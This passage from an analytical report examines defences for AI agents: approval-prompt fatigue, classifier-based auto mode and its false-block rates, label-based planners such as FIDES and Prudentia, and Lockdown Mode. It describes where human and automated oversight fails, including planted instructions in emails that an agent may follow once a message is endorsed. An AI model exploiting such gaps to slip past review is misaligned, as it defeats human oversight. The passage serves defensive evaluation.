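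Some approval prompts don't give the user enough information to decide. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of problems with agents and files. User review contributed to 105 of them, including 80 where the user had turned on automatic approval and 31 where the prompt was uninformative. For example, a request to run a setup script looks routine, but approving it lets any code in the script run. Similarly, if Maria Keller has to approve an email to Jonas Brandt without seeing its text, she can't notice that it contains the word "oncology".

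*Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026), a study of code review, suggests that people become less strict with experience. Reviewers' approval rate for agent-written pull requests rose from 30.1% early on to 36.8% later, while their approval of human-written code fell. They also put less effort into comments. Yu and colleagues consider habit under a growing workload a better explanation than justified trust alone. Code review is slower than answering a permission prompt, so the study supports the general tendency but not a particular error rate for prompts.

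### The study of 1,053 testers

Anthropic's most direct evidence comes from an experiment with 1,053 paid professional testers. A research vendor gave them coding work in a test environment. They knew they were taking part in an evaluation, but not which behaviour the vendor was measuring. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. Nothing dangerous ran, even if the tester approved.

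Anthropic then had auto mode judge the same commands. The table combines the two sets of decisions.

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 (13.6%) |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 (89%) | 116 | 1,053 |

If each tester had acted as a backup to the classifier, reviewing only what auto mode allowed and answering in the same way, they would have caught only six more commands, raising the total from 89.0% to 89.6%.

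Testers caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode's rate stayed flat. The testers' decline is consistent with repetition wearing down attention, but each tester received only one dangerous command, so the figures compare different people. Anthropic doesn't explain how the vendor chose when each tester would receive it. If the timing wasn't random, the testers who had reached 50 prompts may have been people who clicked through prompts faster.

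The study has other limits. Anthropic sells the product that performed best, and the testers had no code, customers or secrets of their own to lose. The study tested dangerous commands in general and didn't report data leaks separately, so 89% can't be read as the share of leaks that auto mode stops. An email that includes a private detail it shouldn't would probably be harder for both people and the classifier to recognise than a clearly dangerous command.

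Anthropic also wrote in March that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who carefully checks every action. The tester study suggests such people are rare, but it doesn't show that careful review is useless.

### Fewer prompts in plainer language

People did much better in an independent experiment on everyday tasks. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond the assigned tasks, such as reading private messages or publicly announcing that the user was travelling. Every prompt described the action in plain language.

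| Arrangement | Prompts per person | Overreach blocked | Time spent on decisions |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user approves every action | 18.0 | 59.6% | 142 seconds |
| A model allows some actions, and the user decides the rest | 10.0 | 53.9% | 120 seconds |
| The user writes standing rules in advance | 10.9 | 39.6% | 129 seconds, including writing the rules |

The sessions were short, and more than a third of the actions were improper, so participants had good reason to stay alert. Both conditions are unusual in daily work. The improper actions also differed from Anthropic's dangerous commands, so the gap between 59.6% and 13.6% doesn't measure the effect of better prompts.

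Fatigue can't explain all the errors in Yan's experiment. In the second arrangement, the model referred all seven improper actions and only three proper ones to the user, so participants had just ten decisions to make. They still approved 46% of the improper actions. Many of the actions looked helpful, such as reading bank transactions to plan a travel budget. In the group that approved every action, 12 of 34 people let the agent read private messages that it didn't need.

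Standing rules gave the weakest protection. Participants could choose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and private data, and chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules. As a result, they were asked about 199 improper actions and approved 133. After correction for multiple comparisons, the difference between standing rules and approving every action remained statistically reliable, but the difference between standing rules and the second arrangement didn't. Yan also assigned some later recruits only to the rules group, which makes the comparison weaker than a fully randomised one.

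People made many mistakes even when a model had removed most of the routine requests, which weakens the case for classifiers that pass doubtful cases to a person. A design that sends every doubtful release to the user therefore depends on the user's judgement as well as their attention.

### False blocks over a long session

Replacing people with software reduces the number of prompts, but small error rates add up. By the same formula as for independent attacks, a check with a false positive rate of *α* wrongly blocks at least one of *n* harmless calls with probability

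1 − (1 − *α*)ⁿ

Auto mode's measured false positive rate was 0.4%. The table also shows a rate ten times lower (0.04%) and the 8.5% rate of auto mode's first stage alone.

| Checked calls in a session | 0.04% | 0.4% | 8.5% |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 0.4% | 4% | 59% |
| 50 | 2% | 18% | 99% |
| 200 | 8% | 55% | almost 100% |
| 1,000 | 33% | 98% | almost 100% |

At a false-block rate of 0.4% per call, a session of 200 checked calls has about a 55% chance of at least one false block. If each block ended the session, more than half of these sessions would fail unnecessarily.

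When auto mode wrongly blocks an action, the agent usually needs only one more attempt, because it can try another route. For example, if it can't upload a file to one service, it may be able to save the file in the project directory. Similarly, an agent that must omit a private detail from an email can often still send the rest.

If the classifier's errors were independent, a session would almost never reach auto mode's limit of three blocks in a row. But a classifier that wrongly blocks one action is likely to block a similar one. If it wrongly blocked half of all retries, about 18% of sessions with 200 calls would reach the limit. If it blocked a tenth of them, fewer than 1% would. The method therefore works only if the agent can find an alternative that the classifier will allow, and some tasks have none. Maria's agent, for example, can't reschedule a call with Brandt without contacting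 Brandt.

At Gusto, one of Anthropic's customers, about 10% of sessions since mid-May 2026 included a denial. Anthropic presents this as evidence that auto mode does useful work without slowing legitimate tasks, but the figure doesn't separate correct denials from mistaken ones. At a false positive rate of 0.4% and about 26 checked calls per session, mistaken denials alone would affect 10% of sessions.

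Anthropic also reports that auto mode users at companies that have adopted it complete about 25% more pull requests. People chose the mode themselves, so more productive users may have been more likely to choose it.

### Planning to need fewer approvals

Systems that enforce labels outside the model can reduce approval requests in another way. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), largely from the Microsoft group behind FIDES, argues that earlier tests overstated the drawbacks of strict rules. Those tests compared a protected agent that received no human help with an unprotected one whose consequential actions would each need approval in many products.

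The researchers propose two measures. The first is the total number of approvals needed across all tasks the agent completes. The second is the share of tasks it completes with at most *k* approvals each. If *vᵢ* is the number of approvals in task *i*, then for *n* tasks

TCR@*k* = (number of completed tasks with *vᵢ* ≤ *k*) / *n*

TCR stands for task completion rate. TCR@0 counts only tasks that the agent completes without any approval, while TCR@∞ counts every completed task.

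Their agent, Prudentia, adds planning to FIDES. In FIDES, the planner doesn't know the security rules, so it may open untrusted text unnecessarily and then need approval for later calls. Prudentia changes this in three ways:

1. It tells the planner which rule applies to each tool and how trusted its context currently is.
2. Before opening a hidden value, the planner is supposed to state why it needs the value and which tools it will call next.
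3. The planner can ask the user to endorse the value, which means accepting it as trusted. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. If no consequential call will follow, the planner opens the email without asking.

Kolluri and colleagues tested four agents on AgentDojo. The agents without labels needed approval for every consequential call, while those with labels needed it only when such a call broke a rule. The researchers assumed the user would approve every call needed to complete a harmless task.

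| Agent | GPT-5: completed | GPT-5: without approval | GPT-5: approvals | GPT-4o: completed | GPT-4o: without approval | GPT-4o: approvals |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plain | 72.3% | 35.1% | 52.0 | 72.2% | 28.0% | 59.4 |
| Plain with labels | 72.3% | 43.4% | 40.4 | 72.2% | 38.4% | 39.4 |
| FIDES | 78.9% | 57.1% | 41.3 | 56.3% | 50.3% | 7.8 |
| Prudentia | 80.0% | 72.7% | 7.3 | 61.4% | 42.5% | 23.8 |

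GPT-5 needed about one approval per eleven completed tasks with Prudentia, compared with roughly one per two with FIDES. GPT-4o, by contrast, needed three times as many approvals with Prudentia as with FIDES and completed fewer tasks without help. GPT-5 reasons at length before acting, which probably helps it plan actions that the rules allow without approval.

On WASP, a benchmark of attacks on web agents, Prudentia needed no approvals and stopped every attack. The user's task was always to post a comment or upvote a post, which doesn't require reading the untrusted text. The result is therefore weak evidence of how Prudentia would perform on tasks that do require it, such as answering an email.

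Planning takes additional computation. With GPT-4o, Prudentia cost 3.9 to 6.3 US cents per task, depending on the environment, compared with 0.4 to 1.1 cents for the plain agent with labels. Prudentia also took more turns, though the researchers did not record elapsed time. They had not yet tried to reduce these costs.

Each approval also matters more when there are fewer of them. If Maria endorses an email that contains a planted instruction, the agent may follow it without asking again, whereas separate approvals would give her several chances to notice. Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of these prompts to future work. They also don't let users give blanket approval for releasing private data, because whether a release is proper depends heavily on the situation.

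However, the rules let a message go out if either the context is trusted or every recipient may read the data, so in a trusted context Prudentia could still mention Maria's oncology appointment to Brandt without asking her. The reduction in approvals is therefore evidence only about defending against planted instructions, not about preventing accidental oversharing.

### Modes that switch risky features off

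A company can avoid most approval requests by removing the features that would cause them. OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode in February 2026 for a small group of people at high risk, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations. OpenAI says most users don't need it. In June, it extended the mode to personal and small business accounts.

Lockdown Mode replaces live browsing with stored pages and disables Deep Research, agent mode and network access for code in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace. In this mode, ChatGPT can't download files for analysis and may not display images in ordinary answers. Users can still upload files and generate images. On personal accounts, the mode also blocks actions in connected apps that conflict with its protections.

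In a company's workspace, an administrator assigns people to a Lockdown Mode role and chooses which apps and actions they may use. OpenAI advises against actions that change data if outsiders might see the result. An email to Brandt is such an action, so a cautious administrator would have to withhold the tool that Maria's agent needs.

Users of personal accounts can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat. This makes it easier to keep it on for other chats, but an impatient user may turn it off in a chat that involves private data. The mode doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, and OpenAI doesn't guarantee that it prevents every leak.

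As a milder measure, OpenAI puts a warning on certain network features but keeps them available, according to its *Elevated Risk labels*. Users lose no functionality, but they have to decide whether to use the features, and they may grow as accustomed to the label as to any other warning.

### The costs side by side

The figures come from different models and tasks, so they can't be ranked against each other. A dash in the table means no comparable figure is available.

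| Defence | Tasks completed | Delay | Set-up work | Approvals |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Redaction | – | 13 milliseconds in one example | choose and test detectors | none |
| Domain allow-list | – | – | list permitted domains | none, unless the user may override a block |
| Session rules | – | about 0.2 milliseconds per check | write rules and exceptions | one per held message |
| Approval of all consequential calls | 72.3% with GPT-5 | the user's response time | little | 52.0 on AgentDojo |
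| Auto mode | – | extra model calls, no time given | optional description of trusted systems | after 3 blocks in a row or 20 in a session |
| MELON | 68.0% with GPT-4o | about twice the model calls | – | none, but an alarm stops the agent |
| FIDES | 78.9% with GPT-5, 57.1% without approvals | extra turns, no time given | label data and write tool rules | 41.3 on AgentDojo |
| Prudentia | 80.0% with GPT-5, 72.7% without approvals | more turns than FIDES, no time given | as for FIDES | 7.3 on AgentDojo |
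| CaMeL | – | – | write tool rules | – |
| FlowSeal | 72.4% on its own benchmark | – | register private records and recipients | 0.71 consent requests per run in one test |
| Lockdown Mode | – | – | one setting, or roles and app permissions | none for disabled features |

Only the GPT-5 figures for full approval, FIDES and Prudentia come from the same test. Kolluri and colleagues report a loss of up to 30% in completed tasks under FIDES and CaMeL on AgentDojo, but don't give separate figures for the two systems.

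Set-up work is the least well measured burden, and none of these studies includes a figure for the hours a company needs to label its data. Waiting for a person may be the largest delay. According to Inc. Russia, an internal Anthropic study found that agents spent 80% of session time waiting for a human reply. That figure covers every kind of reply, including new instructions, so approvals account for only part of it.

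### When people switch a control off

Suppose a control stops a share *c* of leaks while it is on, and users switch it off in a share *u* of sessions. If leaks are equally common in all sessions, it stops

(1 − *u*) × *c*

of them overall. A strict control that stops 99% of leaks but is off in a quarter of sessions stops about 74%. A lenient one that stops 89% and is off in 5% of sessions stops about 85%. With these invented numbers, the strict control is better only if people switch it off in fewer than about 15% of sessions.

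People's reasons for bypassing prompts suggest how a company could keep that share low. Engineers at Nuro, which develops self-driving technology, hated supervising approval prompts, according to Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production*. Before auto mode was available, one of them built a prototype that automatically approved the routine 90% of actions and sent sensitive ones to a person.

Strict rules can also work without asking a person for approval. In Claude Code, a rule that denies a particular tool or command still applies when the user bypasses permission prompts. One mode refuses any action that would normally cause a prompt, which suits scripts that run unattended. Such rules can block legitimate work, but they don't depend on the judgment of a user tired from reviewing many requests.
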